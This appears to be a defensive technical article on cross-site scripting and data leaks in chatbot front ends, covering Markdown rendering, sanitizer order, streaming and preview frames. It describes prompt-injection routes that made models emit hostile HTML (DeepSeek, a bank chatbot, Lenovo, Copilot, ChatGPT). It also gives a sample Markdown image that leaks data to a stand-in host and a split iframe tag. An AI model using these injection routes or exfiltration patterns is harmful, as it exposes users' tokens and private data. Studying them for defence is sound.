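A model's text can become code in the page when it contains characters that have a meaning in HTML, such as the angle bracket that opens a tag or the quotation mark that ends an attribute. The front end can escape these characters by replacing each with a sequence that the browser displays as the literal character, such as `&lt;` for `<`. If it leaves one unescaped, whoever influenced the model's answer may be able to add their own HTML to the page.

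Researchers have documented a failure at four of the five steps:

| Step | What happens to the text | Documented failure |
|---|---|---|
| Parsing | Markdown becomes HTML | AnythingLLM did not escape the descriptions of images |
| Raw HTML | Tags written by the model either appear as text or become elements | Two customer chats turned them into elements and checked only the addresses |
| Extensions | Add-ons draw formulas and diagrams | Open WebUI pasted a formula's source into the page after an error |
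| Sanitizing | A sanitizer removes dangerous elements and attributes | Open WebUI ran its sanitizer before the parser |
| Insertion | The browser builds the elements | Any script left over from the earlier steps can run |

### Two customer chats

In August 2026, Escape, which sells automated security testing, reported the same stored XSS vulnerability in the customer chats of two unrelated companies. Its testing agent found both cases. Escape does not name the companies, so outsiders can't confirm the cases. But the libraries involved are public, so a developer can check the explanation by combining them in the same way.

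Both chats used react-markdown, a library that parses Markdown and builds page elements from it. CommonMark, a Markdown specification, allows raw HTML, so a model might write `H<sub>2</sub>O` to make the 2 a subscript. By default, react-markdown displays these tags as text, which is safe but looks untidy. Both companies had added rehype-raw, a plugin that turns the tags into real elements.

Neither company had put a sanitizer after the plugin. The only remaining protection was react-markdown's link filter, which checks that an address begins with something harmless, such as "https:" or "mailto:". The filter works from a list of HTML attributes that hold addresses, including the src attribute of images and frames. But a frame can also have a srcdoc attribute, which holds the text of a whole document instead of an address. The list did not include srcdoc, so an attack could work like this:

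1. The attacker gets the model to write a frame with a script inside its srcdoc attribute.
2. rehype-raw turns this text into a frame element.
3. The link filter finds no address to check and leaves srcdoc unchanged.
4. The browser loads the contents of srcdoc as a new document and runs the script.
5. The frame is not sandboxed, so the script has the chat's own origin. It can read the surrounding page, including any access tokens within reach of a script and the API keys stored in the page's settings.

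According to Escape, most filters don't look for script elements, because browsers don't run those that a page inserts through innerHTML. That rule doesn't protect the page here, since the browser parses the contents of srcdoc as a new document.

### Failures at the other steps

In Open WebUI, a user with the right permission can create a "model" by giving an existing language model a new name, instructions and description. The front end displays the description on the chat page. Fluid Attacks' *Server side cross-site scripting In open-webui*, a copy of the project's advisory, explains how a description could carry a script. The description came from a user, not a language model, but it went through the same kind of chain.

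The front end escaped every angle bracket in the description to sanitize it, then parsed the result as Markdown and inserted it as HTML. Markdown links use square and round brackets, so the escaping left them unchanged. After this step, the parser turned them into working links. If a link's address began with "javascript:", the browser would run the rest of the address as a script when someone clicked it.

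This flaw, CVE-2026-44721, affected versions 0.3.5 to 0.8.12. In version 0.9.0, the maintainers added a second sanitizer, DOMPurify, after the parser. They had made the same mistake elsewhere. Corgea's *Open WebUI has Stored XSS in Pending User Overlay* shows DOMPurify running before the parser in the notice for users awaiting approval. Enginsight's *CVE-2026-45665* describes the same order in the site-wide banner, where a malicious administrator could use it against the primary administrator. The maintainers fixed the banner in version 0.8.0 and the model descriptions only in a later release.

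An older flaw in Open WebUI shows another way a sanitizer and a parser can treat the same text differently. In version 0.1.105, the front end did not escape HTML inside code blocks, because the page was supposed to display it literally. KoreLogic's *KL-001-2024-005* (2024) describes a prompt that made the model write an uneven number of code-block markers. The sanitizer apparently treated some HTML as code, while the parser placed it outside any code block, where it ran. A sanitizer that works on the parser's output does not need to determine where code blocks end.

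The formula flaw, CVE-2026-70492, was in Open WebUI's error handling. Open WebUI's developers had set KaTeX, the library that draws its formulas, to tolerate invalid ones. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3650* (2026), this setting did not cover a formula nested so deeply that KaTeX ran out of working memory. When that happened, the front end tried to display the original formula as text but inserted it as HTML, including any tags it contained. Version 0.10.0, which fixed several of the socket flaws, introduced this one, and version 0.11.0 fixed it by escaping the formula before inserting it.

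The demonstration used 100,000 levels of nesting, so the message was over 200,000 characters long. A limit on message length might have blocked it, but a shorter formula may also cause the error.

OSV's *GHSA-gf5m-wcrh-7928* (2026) rates the description flaw's severity at 7.3 out of 10, while the formula flaw has 8.7. The ratings differ in only one setting, which records whether the damage spreads beyond the flawed component. Both flaws run a script in another user's browser, so it is hard to see why that setting should differ. The formula flaw is still more serious in practice, because its victim need only open a chat, whereas the description flaw's victim must click a link.

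Extensions that draw diagrams can create similar vulnerabilities. Escape cites OneUptime, a monitoring product that used the diagram library Mermaid at a permissive security setting. That setting let Mermaid's command for making part of a diagram clickable run a script wherever OneUptime displayed Markdown, including public status pages.

AnythingLLM, an application for chatting with one's own documents, made its mistake in the parser. A Markdown image has a description, which HTML stores in an attribute called alt. AnythingLLM copied the description there without escaping it. Suppose an image of a pipe has the description `5" pipe`. The result would be:

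```
<img src="pipe.png" alt="5" pipe">
```

The browser takes the quotation mark after the 5 as the end of the description and reads "pipe" as the start of another attribute. An attacker could instead put an event handler there, an attribute whose script runs when something happens, such as an image failing to load.

AnythingLLM's developers ran the parser's output through DOMPurify nearly everywhere as a second defence, which would normally have removed the event handler. But NVD's *CVE-2026-41318 Detail* reports that they left it out for chart captions, the text a model writes around a chart. An attacker could plant instructions in a shared document, and if the model followed them in a caption, a script would run in the browser of anyone who opened the conversation. Version 1.12.1 fixed the flaw. MITRE's *CVE-2026-32626* describes a related flaw that affected replies while they were still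 streaming.

### How hostile text gets into an answer

An attacker can get code into the page by asking the model to write it. Embrace The Red's *DeepSeek AI* describes a 2024 test that asked DeepSeek's chatbot to list well-known test strings for XSS. The page ran one of them, which revealed the flaw even though the prompt contained no HTML.

The researcher then found a way to attack another user through DeepSeek's document upload. A text file contained HTML in base64, an encoding that represents data as letters, digits and a few symbols. The file also contained an instruction for the model to decode this text and write only the result. When the researcher uploaded the file, the page ran the script in the decoded HTML, which displayed the access token from localStorage, enough to take over an account. The demonstration did not send the token anywhere, but a script that can read an access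 token can usually send it too. DeepSeek fixed the flaw a day after the report.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian (2026), in *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation*, classify this as reflected XSS, in which the application returns the script immediately instead of storing it. They argue that a language model usually does not create the underlying flaw and only provides a new route to it. DeepSeek therefore needed to fix its front end, since the model had only decoded some text, following instructions in the file.

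Positive Security's *Banking AI XSS* (2026) describes a bank's chatbot that accepted hostile text by three routes. The testers first typed a request to add a payee whose name contained an HTML image with an event handler. They then hid the name and instructions as white text in a PDF invoice. When a user uploaded the invoice and asked the chatbot to add the payee, the script ran in the user's banking session.

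The testers' third route was the reference field of a European bank transfer, which is limited to 140 characters and can't contain angle brackets. They sent two one-cent payments, with the HTML split between the references and the forbidden characters written as abbreviations. The model joined the two parts and restored the missing characters.

Positive Security writes that a victim could trigger the script by asking for the month's transactions. But in the published demonstration, the user's question repeated some of the attacker's instructions, because the testers did not want to send many suspicious payments through a live bank. They showed that a payment reference can deliver the script, but not that an ordinary question is enough to trigger it.

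Software add-ons can also cause a model to write text that runs as code. Escape describes a flaw in NoteGen, a note-taking application, in which a reference file supplied with a "skill" contained instructions for the model to write HTML. The HTML then ran in the application's window, which had more privileges than an ordinary web page.

### Do users only attack themselves?

An attacker can use this kind of flaw against other people if they open a transcript containing the hostile text, or if the model reads text the attacker wrote while answering them. If only the user's own prompt can trigger the flaw, it is fair to object that the script runs in a browser the user already controls. The bank at first made this objection to Positive Security, saying that the flaw was "scoped only to your user" and couldn't be used against other customers. It accepted the finding after further explanation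 and fixed the flaw within about two days of the report.

Cybernews' *Lenovo “Lena” AI Chatbot Exploited via XSS Prompt Injection* (2025) describes an attack on Lenovo's customer-service chatbot that began with a single 400-character prompt. The prompt asked about a laptop and told the chatbot to end its answer with an HTML image. The image was designed to fail to load, which would trigger an event handler that sent the reader's cookies to the attacker. Readers could include support staff, who open transcripts as part of their job.

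Lenovo's server saved the answer with the conversation. The attacker then asked to speak to a person, and when a support agent opened the chat, the script ran again in the agent's browser. Cybernews warns that the attacker could use the agent's session cookie to log in to the support system and perhaps read other customers' chats. Setting the HttpOnly attribute on the cookie would have prevented this theft, though the script could still have acted from the agent's page.

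Cybernews adds that an attacker might be able to run system commands and install backdoors, but its researchers didn't try. A script in a web page can't do this by itself, so the attacker would need another flaw or a powerful function in the support system.

The bank's chatbot also automatically passed one of the testers' conversations to a human agent, but Positive Security did not test whether the HTML ran on the agent's side. The evidence from Open WebUI is stronger because the person who reported the formula flaw stole an access token through a shared chat that an administrator account had opened. Quarkslab's *From Prompt to Pwned* also describes a chain of model and web flaws that led from an ordinary account to an administrator's.

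Other customers can be the victims too. ferreiraklet, in *How I Made an AI Steal Session Tokens for Me*, describes an unnamed dashboard for property businesses, with a chat that used SSE. Its front end turned a private shorthand in the model's answers into HTML elements with any attributes the text specified. The researcher also found that the server let any customer rename another customer's business. The attack combined the two:

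1. The attacker changes the victim's business name to shorthand for a frame containing a script.
2. The victim asks an ordinary question, such as what is on the calendar for the business.
3. The model includes the business name in its answer.
4. The front end turns the name into a frame, and the script sends the victim's access token to the attacker.

The access token lasted 30 days. The victim didn't share a transcript, open a strange document or click a link. ferreiraklet's post is undated and, like Escape's, describes a product that readers can't examine, but it gives the requests and responses for each step.

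### Leaking data through an image

An answer can reveal private data without running a script. When a page contains an image, the browser requests it from the address given, and anyone who controls that server can read the address in its logs. If hostile instructions make the model put private data into the address, the browser delivers the data:

```
![chart](https://quiz.example/chart.png?note=Invoice+overdue)
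```

The image is written in ordinary Markdown, so a front end that escapes all raw HTML will still load it. Many sanitizers will also allow it, because an image with an "https:" address contains no script. The attacker can't act as the user, as they could with XSS, but they can receive any data that the model can read and put in the image's address.

An attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot could expose a company's email and files. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack that began with a link to Microsoft's own website. Copilot's search page treated part of the link as a prompt and ran it as soon as the page opened. The prompt was an instruction to find an email and put its subject line into the address of an image. Subject lines sometimes contain login codes, as in Varonis' example.

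Microsoft's Copilot turned HTML in its answers into harmless text, but only after the answer was complete, when the browser had already requested the image. The page's Content Security Policy also allowed images only from certain sites, so the attacker could not load an image directly from their own server.

But the policy allowed images from Bing, Microsoft's search engine. Bing can search for a picture by its address, and Bing's servers fetch the picture. The attacker therefore used a Bing address that contained the address of their own server, and put the subject line in that second address. The browser sent the request to Bing, which forwarded the subject line to the attacker. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and has fixed it.

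Some developers load outside images through their own server to hide the user's network address. This doesn't stop the leak if the server fetches any address it receives, because it then sends the private data to the attacker, as Bing did. The simplest protection for chat.example is to display outside images as links and load only images that it stores itself. A user can still click a link that contains private data, but the browser won't send the data automatically.

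### Fixing the chain

Cybernews recommends filtering what users type, including a strict list of allowed characters. This is a weak defence for a chatbot because the model can rebuild what the filter removed, as it did with the base64 text and the payment references. The bank's chatbot also rejected the best-known event handler for images but accepted a rarer one. ferreiraklet got past a firewall by adding about 8 kilobytes of filler to each request, probably because the firewall inspected only the beginning. The reliable fixes apply to the HTML that comes out of the chain, and they cover different flaws:

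| Flaw | Escape raw HTML | Sanitize last, with an allowlist | CSP that forbids inline scripts and outside images |
|---|---|---|---|
| Customer chats: document inside a frame | Stopped | Stopped | Inline script blocked |
| Open WebUI: link in a description | Not stopped, because the link is ordinary Markdown | Stopped | Stopped |
| Open WebUI: formula error | Not stopped, because the formula skips this step | Stopped, if the sanitizer also covers formulas | Inline script blocked |
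| AnythingLLM: image description | Not stopped, because the image is ordinary Markdown | Stopped | Inline script blocked |
| Data in an image address | Not stopped, if Markdown images work | Stopped, if the list excludes outside images | Stopped, unless a permitted site forwards the request |

Escaping raw HTML is the strongest fix where it applies, because the browser never turns the model's tags into elements. In a front end built on react-markdown, developers usually only have to delete rehype-raw. Markdown tables, links and code blocks still work, but `H<sub>2</sub>O` appears with its tags visible.

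The sanitizer should run last, after the parser and every extension, and keep only what is on a list. For chat.example, the list might be:

```
elements:    p, br, h1 to h4, strong, em, ul, ol, li, blockquote,
             pre, code, table, thead, tbody, tr, th, td, a
attributes:  href on a, if the address starts with https: or mailto:
```

A list of forbidden items is weaker than a list of allowed ones because developers have to think of every dangerous attribute and can easily miss one, such as srcdoc. Escape also warns that a sanitizer at the end of the chain may remove the output of extensions such as diagrams. Developers then move the sanitizer earlier to get the diagrams working again, and it ends up running before the step it was meant to check. They should instead check each attribute of the elements a diagram needs, then add those elements to the allowed list.

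Cybernews advises sanitizing text before storing it, while Escape advises sanitizing it wherever an application displays it. Escape's advice is safer because a stored answer may appear in the chat, a support console and an email, and each may parse it differently. The Open WebUI description also shows that text that is harmless in storage can become dangerous when the front end parses it.

Browsers have begun to include their own sanitizer. A page normally passes HTML to DOMPurify, which parses it, cleans it and returns text that the browser then parses again. The second parse can differ from the first, and attackers have used such differences to get scripts past sanitizers. Braun's *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()* explains why the built-in sanitizer cleans and inserts the HTML with one command, setHTML(). The browser parses the text once, for the exact place where it will appear.

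According to MDN's *Element*, setHTML() always removes scripts, frames and event handlers, even if the developer's list allows them. In an example from Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* (2026), the default settings also remove an image. Removing images would stop leaks through image addresses, but a developer who allows them will bring the risk back.

Firefox has supported setHTML() since version 148, and Chrome and Edge since version 146. Safari did not support it in August 2026, according to web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API*. A request to add it to Safari's engine, *Implement Sanitizer API* (Lee, 2025), was still open in April 2026. A public chatbot therefore still needs a library such as DOMPurify for Safari users. Front ends that build elements directly, as react-markdown does, have no innerHTML assignment for setHTML() to replace. Their developers can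 use the rehype-sanitize plugin after rehype-raw instead.

Trusted Types help developers find places where they forgot to sanitize text. When a site turns this feature on, the browser refuses ordinary text in innerHTML, srcdoc and similar places. It accepts only values that have passed through a function the developers approved, which can run DOMPurify. If a new chart component skips the sanitizer, it fails visibly instead of creating a flaw. The approved function still has to be safe, because the browser does not check what it does. Web platform features explorer's *February 2026 release notes* (2026) list Trusted Types as newly available, a label for features that have reached all the main browsers.

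A site can allow setHTML() and block the unsafe ways to insert HTML. In Safari, the DOMPurify fallback has to run inside an approved function, or the browser will reject its output too.

A Content Security Policy can limit the damage if hostile HTML still gets through. For chat.example, the server might send:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self';
  form-action 'self'; frame-src 'none'; require-trusted-types-for 'script'
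```

This policy limits scripts, images and other content to chat.example's own origin. It also blocks inline scripts (those written directly into the HTML), including event handlers and "javascript:" links. The form rule stops a planted form from sending a user's password to another site, and the last rule turns on Trusted Types. The bank had no such policy, so the testers' script could load more code from their server and send data back to it.

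Mozilla's developers, who helped start the CSP standard in 2009, write that too few sites have adopted it, because existing sites need large changes and continuing expert review. A new chatbot can avoid much of that work by starting with a strict policy. Its developers should still check whether any outside site they later allow fetches URLs on request, as Bing did.

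## What changes when the text is rendered in pieces?

The advice to sanitize last is easy to follow once an answer is complete. But a chatbot that streams its answers, whatever transport it uses, renders the text many times before then, and the browser acts on each version immediately. A version may end in the middle of a tag, or contain a real image where the finished answer only shows code.

### One answer in five pieces

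Suppose chat.example sends this answer in five pieces, where \n starts a new line:

```
1  "See the [altitude table](https://chat.exam"
2  "ple/altitude).\n\n![Boiling curve](https://chat.example/cur"
3  "ve.png)\n\n```\nboil = 100 - "
4  "metres / 300\n"
5  "```\nThis is a rough rule."
```

The front end could convert each piece to HTML on its own and append the result. It could instead add each piece to the text so far and re-render the whole answer. Or it could use a stateful parser, which remembers, for example, that it is inside a code block and continues from there. Libraries differ in the details, but the page would look roughly like this:

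| After piece | Appending each piece | Re-rendering everything | Stateful parser |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Raw Markdown: `[altitude table](https://chat.exam` | The same raw Markdown | The words "altitude table", with no address yet |
| 2 | More raw Markdown | A working link, then the unfinished image as raw Markdown | A working link, but no image yet |
| 3 | "ve.png)" as text, then a code block with "boil = 100 -" | The image, then a code block with "boil = 100 -" | The same |
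| 4 | "metres / 300" as ordinary text below the code block | The whole formula in the code block | The same |
| 5 | The last sentence in a second code block | The last sentence as ordinary text | The same |

If the front end parses each piece of Markdown separately and appends the result, a link or image split across pieces never renders, because no single piece contains all of it. Chrome for Developers' *How LLMs stream responses* warns against parsing Markdown piece by piece for this reason. Appending works well only for plain text, which the front end can add without parsing.

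Streamdown, a library for displaying streamed Markdown, completes any unfinished Markdown before re-rendering the text. According to Streamdown's *Unterminated Block Parsing*, an unfinished link gets a placeholder address that leads nowhere, and an unfinished image appears as a loading animation. Just adding the missing bracket would be riskier, because after piece 1 it would create a working link to https://chat.exam, a different site. Real addresses have the same problem, since one ending in .com could be cut off at .co. With an image, the browser could send a request to the other site without a click.

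### A tag split between two pieces

Suppose chat.example has a filter that rejects any piece containing a frame, and the model writes one in two pieces:

```
1  "<ifr"
2  "ame src='https://quiz.example/'></iframe>"
```

When a frame's opening tag is split between two pieces, the front end's filter approves both because it checks each piece separately and neither contains the complete tag. If the front end then gives each piece to the browser as a separate fragment of HTML, the browser drops the half tag and displays most of the rest as text. But if the front end joins the pieces before rendering them, or uses an HTML parser that keeps the half tag until the next piece arrives, the frame appears.

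A sanitizer that returns cleaned HTML would usually drop the half tag as well, which damages the answer but does no other harm. A filter that only approves or rejects each piece, and forwards approved pieces unchanged, lets the frame through.

Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) recommends checking all the text received so far. In its sample code, the sanitizer DOMPurify checks the accumulated text whenever a new piece arrives. If DOMPurify removes anything, the front end stops rendering the answer. Otherwise, it passes the new piece to a stateful parser, streaming-markdown. This catches the split frame because DOMPurify checks the whole tag before the parser receives the second piece.

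However, the sample runs DOMPurify on the Markdown before parsing it, the order that caused flaws in Open WebUI. DOMPurify would miss a Markdown link to a "javascript:" address, for example, so the parser has to reject such addresses itself. DOMPurify also can't recognise a Markdown code block, so if a user asks how to write a script tag, the front end may stop halfway through a harmless explanation. The check for tags adds little here, since *Streaming Markdown* (thetarnav, 2024) lists HTML tags among the features that streaming-markdown does not support.

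In newer advice for Chrome developers, Nalpas (2026) puts the sanitizer after the parser. The parser builds the answer off-screen, and after each piece the front end copies a sanitized version to the page. The order is right, but developers will have to adapt the sample code because it calls sanitize(), which does not appear in the current HTML standard (WHATWG, *Dynamic markup insertion*) and probably comes from an earlier draft.

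Building the answer off-screen doesn't necessarily delay image requests. When a script creates an ordinary image element and sets its address, the browser requests the image even if the element is not yet on the page. A sanitizer that later removes the image from the off-screen copy can't prevent that request.

Developers can prevent the browser from requesting forbidden images by checking addresses inside the parser. The streaming-markdown library lets them supply their own function for setting attributes such as a link's address, and that function can compare each address with an allowlist before setting it. The front end then needs to check each address only once.

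### The cost of starting again

If the front end re-renders the whole text, it handles one piece at the first update, two at the second and so on. For an answer of n pieces, the total is:

```
1 + 2 + 3 + … + n = n(n + 1)/2, or about n²/2
```

When the front end parses the whole answer again each time a piece arrives, the five-piece answer requires parsing 15 pieces instead of 5, which nobody would notice. An answer of 3,000 pieces requires parsing about 4.5 million instead of 3,000. At four characters per piece, the front end parses 18 million characters to display a 12,000-character answer. The sanitizer and the browser's HTML parser repeat their work in the same way, and according to Chrome for Developers, the page may also have to redo slow formatting, such as colouring code.

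Re-rendering is still popular because it is simple. The library in TanStack's *AI Streaming* parses the complete text at every update, so developers have no parser state to coordinate or discard. They can also reduce the amount of parsing by updating the page less often. If the front end waits for ten new pieces before each update, the total parsed for a 3,000-piece response falls to about 450,000 pieces, and the reader hardly notices the delay.

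Another way is to divide the answer into blocks, such as paragraphs, and re-parse only the current block. The Rust library mdstream, for example, never changes a block once it is complete. If the 3,000 pieces form 30 equal paragraphs, the parser processes 30 × 5,050, or about 150,000, pieces in total, counting repeats. The saving is smaller for a long table or code block, because it counts as one block.

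The front end can sanitize each finished block once if later text cannot change that block. Ordinary Markdown breaks this condition because it lets an author put a link's address at the end of the document, so a late piece can turn words in the first paragraph into a link. The streaming-markdown parser by thetarnav does not support such links.

The HTML standard now includes a method, streamHTML(), that lets a script write HTML to an element piece by piece. The browser keeps the parser's state between pieces and sanitizes the markup as it parses, so a tag split across pieces can't get past the sanitizer and earlier pieces don't have to be parsed again. Models usually write Markdown, though, so a chatbot would still need a streaming converter to turn it into HTML first.

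In September 2026, Chrome for Developers' *Declarative partial updates* (2026) listed the command as available in Chrome and Edge only behind a developer setting, with a launch planned for Chrome 155. Firefox and Safari did not support it. A substitute library accepts the same commands but inserts the text only when all of it has arrived, so users don't see it stream in. The article's streaming examples use streamHTMLUnsafe(), which does not sanitize HTML by default, so copying one into a chatbot could create an XSS flaw.

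### Is a check of the finished answer too late?

Escape argues that when a chat streams its answers, a sanitizer that checks the finished document runs after the browser has already rendered the content. This is true of any front end that inserts unsanitized content during the stream and sanitizes it at the end. Microsoft 365 Copilot had this fault, and the browser requested the attacker's image before sanitization began.

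Sometimes the finished answer contains nothing to clean up. For example, a model might explain how to write an image in Markdown:

```
Write `![chart](https://quiz.example/chart.png)` to add an image.
```

When Markdown image syntax sits between two backticks, the finished page displays it as literal code. In standard Markdown, though, a backtick without a partner is an ordinary character. If the front end re-renders after the image syntax is complete but before the second backtick arrives, the page briefly contains a real image, and the browser requests it. A sanitizer that checks only the finished answer won't find an image, and neither will a person reading the transcript. An attacker who plants instructions for the model could use this to send out private data, leaving only a harmless-looking code sample.

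Streamdown prevents this leak by adding the missing backtick, and streaming-markdown does so by treating the text as code from the first backtick onwards. This early styling was meant only to make the page look better while text arrives.

Sanitizers still work on streamed output, but they have to run before every insertion. Escape's argument does not apply to a front end that does this. The repair Escape recommends, the rehype-sanitize plugin, works this way in react-markdown because it filters the elements each time the component renders. In the example above, it would remove the temporary image if its list excluded outside images. A stateful parser that checks each address before using it also acts early enough, as does streamHTML().

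Streamdown also includes rehype-sanitize and a second plugin that can restrict links and image sources. Its default settings are permissive, so developers who want to prevent data leaks through images have to tighten them.

Deleting an element does not undo its effects. Even if the front end removes an image a tenth of a second after rendering it, any private data in the image's URL has already reached the server that the URL points to.

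### Filters that withdraw an answer

Many chatbots also use an output filter, a service that checks the model's answer for forbidden content such as threats or copyrighted text. It can hold the text back until the check is complete, or show the text at once and withdraw it later if necessary. Microsoft, AWS and NVIDIA document both approaches:

| Filter and mode | What the user receives | Documented size or delay |
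|---|---|---|
| Microsoft, default | Only text that has passed the check | Depends on the size of the buffer |
| Microsoft, asynchronous | Text at once, with a possible stop later | The stop comes within about 1,000 characters |
| AWS Bedrock, default | Only text that has passed the check | One or more pieces at a time |
| AWS Bedrock, asynchronous | Text at once, with later pieces blocked if necessary | No stated limit |
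| AWS Bedrock agents | Text in groups, with a check for each | 50 characters by default |
| NVIDIA NeMo Guardrails, default for streams | Text before the check | 200 text tokens, with 50 carried over |

Microsoft's *Content filtering* described asynchronous filtering as a preview for approved customers, but Microsoft's later *Content streaming* lists it as available to everyone. Buffering removes much of the benefit of streaming, so developers have a reason to turn on the asynchronous filter. AI SDK's *Azure OpenAI Slow to Stream* notes that answers arrive slowly and in big chunks, and that some users fixed this by switching to the asynchronous filter.

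In Microsoft's sample of a blocked answer, a user asks for song lyrics. The service streams them immediately, then reports a copyright violation in 991 characters it has already sent. At 50 text tokens per second and four characters per token, 1,000 characters take five seconds to arrive. An attack through an image needs far less text. The example in the previous section, with an invoice's subject line in the image's address, was 61 characters long.

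Buffering could let the filter stop such an image, but only if the filter is set to detect it. The categories in Microsoft's samples are hate, sexual content, violence, self-harm and copyrighted text, none of which covers an ordinary image address containing private data. AWS's filter can mask sensitive information, which is closer to what is needed, but AWS's *Configure streaming response behavior to filter content* warns that masking does not work in asynchronous mode.

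Filters have the same problem with boundaries as sanitizers. The 61-character image doesn't fit in one of the 50-character groups described in AWS's *StreamingConfigurations*, so a filter that processed each group alone would check only part of the address at a time. Overlapping windows reduce this problem. With the defaults in NVIDIA's *Output Rail Streaming Configuration*, each check also includes the last 50 text tokens of the previous group, so a forbidden phrase of up to about 50 tokens appears whole in at least one check. A longer passage can still be split between checks.

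NVIDIA's default setting sends text to the user before it is checked. A developer can have the text checked first, but at 50 tokens per second the user would then wait four seconds for the first 200 tokens. Checking smaller groups of tokens shortens the wait but requires more checks, each with less context.

Microsoft recommends its default mode for customer-facing chatbots in regulated industries, and the asynchronous mode for uses such as internal tools. In asynchronous mode, the front end has to remove text that the user can already see, so chat.example would need a message type for withdrawing an answer. Its server would also need to delete the text from the saved conversation, or it would return when the user reloaded the page. If chat.example loads outside images at all, it should load them only after the answer has passed every check.

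### After a lost connection

Suppose the connection breaks just after chat.example has sent piece 3 of the answer about boiling water. The server may have no record of whether the browser received the piece, so it sends it again when the browser reconnects. If the front end adds the piece a second time, the text contains an extra code marker, which the parser treats as the end of the code block. The page then displays the formula as ordinary text and puts the final sentence in a new code block.

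Here the duplicate only spoils the layout. But if the code block contained an HTML example and the front end accepted raw HTML, the example's tags would become real elements. Losing a piece that contains a code marker could have the same effect. A server-side filter would not catch this, because it checked the model's original text, not the altered text in the browser. A sanitizer that runs before every insertion would still remove anything dangerous.

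Numbering the pieces prevents both errors:

```
on piece(answer, number, text):
    if number is below the next expected number:
        discard the piece, because the page already has it
    if number is above the next expected number:
        fetch the whole answer so far and render it from the start
    otherwise:
        add the text and expect the next number
```

With SSE, the event identifiers that EventSource already reports can serve as the numbers. A WebSocket has no such feature, so developers have to add the numbers and recovery themselves. In either case, the server must check that the reconnecting user is allowed to read the answer.

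If the user refreshes the page while an answer is streaming, a stateful parser loses its state. It can't resume from the next piece because it has no record of, for example, an open code block, so the server has to replay the answer from the beginning.

### When the saved answer looks different

A chatbot may use one parser for the live answer and another for saved transcripts. Different rendering paths can have different flaws. In AnythingLLM, one flaw affected replies while they were streaming and another affected chart captions. If a front end uses streaming-markdown for live answers and a full Markdown parser for saved ones, HTML tags that appear as harmless text during the chat may become elements when someone reopens it.

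If the front end follows Chrome's advice to stop rendering a suspicious answer, the server may still receive and save the rest. The user never sees the dangerous part, but it may run in the browser of a support agent who later opens the transcript. Escape notes that companies test support consoles less than the pages their customers use, although the people who use them often have more access.

chat.example should save the model's original Markdown rather than the sanitized HTML. WHATWG warns that sanitized HTML is no longer safe to trust once a program has turned its elements back into text, because the browser then has to parse it again. If the live page and the support console share one rendering function, fixing it protects both. When the front end stops an answer, it should also notify the server, which can then mark the saved copy so that other pages can withhold it.

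## Can generated code escape its preview frame?

Some chatbots can run the web pages that their models write. A user of chat.example might ask for a page with a slider that shows the boiling point of water at any altitude. The model writes the HTML and JavaScript, and the front end runs the page beside the conversation.

A sanitizer doesn't help here, because it would remove the script that makes the slider work. The front end has to run the script but keep it away from the user's account. In autumn 2026, researchers published two flaws in ChatGPT's version of this feature. One allowed an attacker's script to get into the signed-in ChatGPT page, and the other allowed a preview to send chat data to an outside server.

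### How a preview frame works

The usual protection starts with a sandboxed frame, an embedded page from which the browser withholds some abilities. By default the browser withholds nearly all of them, and the developers give back the ones they need by name:

| Permission | What the frame may then do | Does the slider page need it? |
|---|---|---|
| allow-scripts | Run JavaScript | Yes |
| allow-same-origin | Keep the origin of its own address | No |
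| allow-popups | Open new windows | No |
| allow-popups-to-escape-sandbox | Open new windows that have no sandbox | No |

Unless a sandboxed preview frame has the `allow-same-origin` permission, the browser gives it a temporary origin that matches no other and reports that origin as "null". If the frame has both `allow-scripts` and `allow-same-origin`, a preview loaded from the chatbot's own origin, such as https://chat.example, could read the chatbot's page and even remove its own sandbox.

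Developers therefore also serve previews from a separate origin, such as https://chat-preview.example. The same-origin policy then protects the chatbot even if someone later adds allow-same-origin, perhaps to let a generated page store data. A subdomain such as preview.chat.example is weaker because it belongs to the same site as the chatbot, so its requests to the chatbot could carry SameSite cookies.

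The preview's script can still try to open a WebSocket to chat.example. The browser will send "null" or https://chat-preview.example in the Origin header, so the server's Origin check will block the connection unless the developers have put that value on the allowlist.

The main page and the preview usually need to exchange some information. For example, the preview may send its height so that the main page can make room for it. They can use postMessage, the browser function that also let other websites send commands to Open WebUI's page. The receiving page gets the sender's origin and a reference to the window that sent the message.

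The sandbox has no permission that controls messages. Any frame that can run scripts can send messages to the page around it, and every message listener in that page receives them, including those added by third-party libraries. Each listener must therefore check whether the sender is trusted.

### A graph that opened a way in

The first attack began with an ordinary public link to a shared ChatGPT conversation. When a signed-in user opened it, the attacker's script could run with that user's access to ChatGPT. Goyal (2026) published the details in *Do the Math* on 28 October for the security company Parameter.

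ChatGPT ran its previews in a restricted frame on a separate address, and this worked as intended: a script in the preview could not read the page around it. The researchers got past it with the help of an interactive graph in the same conversation:

1. To draw the graph, ChatGPT loaded a mathematics library called MathLive into the main page. MathLive also began listening for messages about its on-screen keyboard.
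2. The preview sent a message containing a new keyboard layout. MathLive accepted it because its origin policy was "none", which meant that it took messages from any origin.
3. A keyboard layout could contain HTML. When the preview sent a second message telling MathLive to show the keyboard, MathLive put the attacker's HTML into the main page through innerHTML.
4. The HTML created a frame whose srcdoc attribute held a whole document. This frame had no sandbox, and because the main page had created it, the browser gave it the origin https://chatgpt.com.
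5. ChatGPT's Content Security Policy blocked scripts written directly into the new frame but allowed scripts from YouTube. The attacker got YouTube to return a script that contained the attacker's code.

In the third step, MathLive passed the HTML through a helper function named createHTML, which looked like a sanitizer but only marked the text as trusted and returned it unchanged. Trusted Types would not have caught this if the site had approved that function.

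The fourth step used the same trick as the attack Escape described on the two customer chats, but the researchers also needed YouTube because ChatGPT's policy was stricter.

The YouTube address used JSONP, an old method of sharing data between sites. A page requests the data as a script and names one of its own functions in the address, and the returned script calls that function with the data. The researchers put code where the function name goes. YouTube's server rejected it, but the error reply was also a script and included the rejected text, so the browser ran the code.

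### What the researchers could read

The researchers' script listed the victim's conversations and opened one the victim had never shared. It then sent a small part of the text to a server the researchers controlled. 송 (2026), in *챗GPT 공유 링크 열고 버튼 한 번 누르면 공격자 코드 실행*, reports that the browser sent the text in an image request, as in the leaks that need no script.

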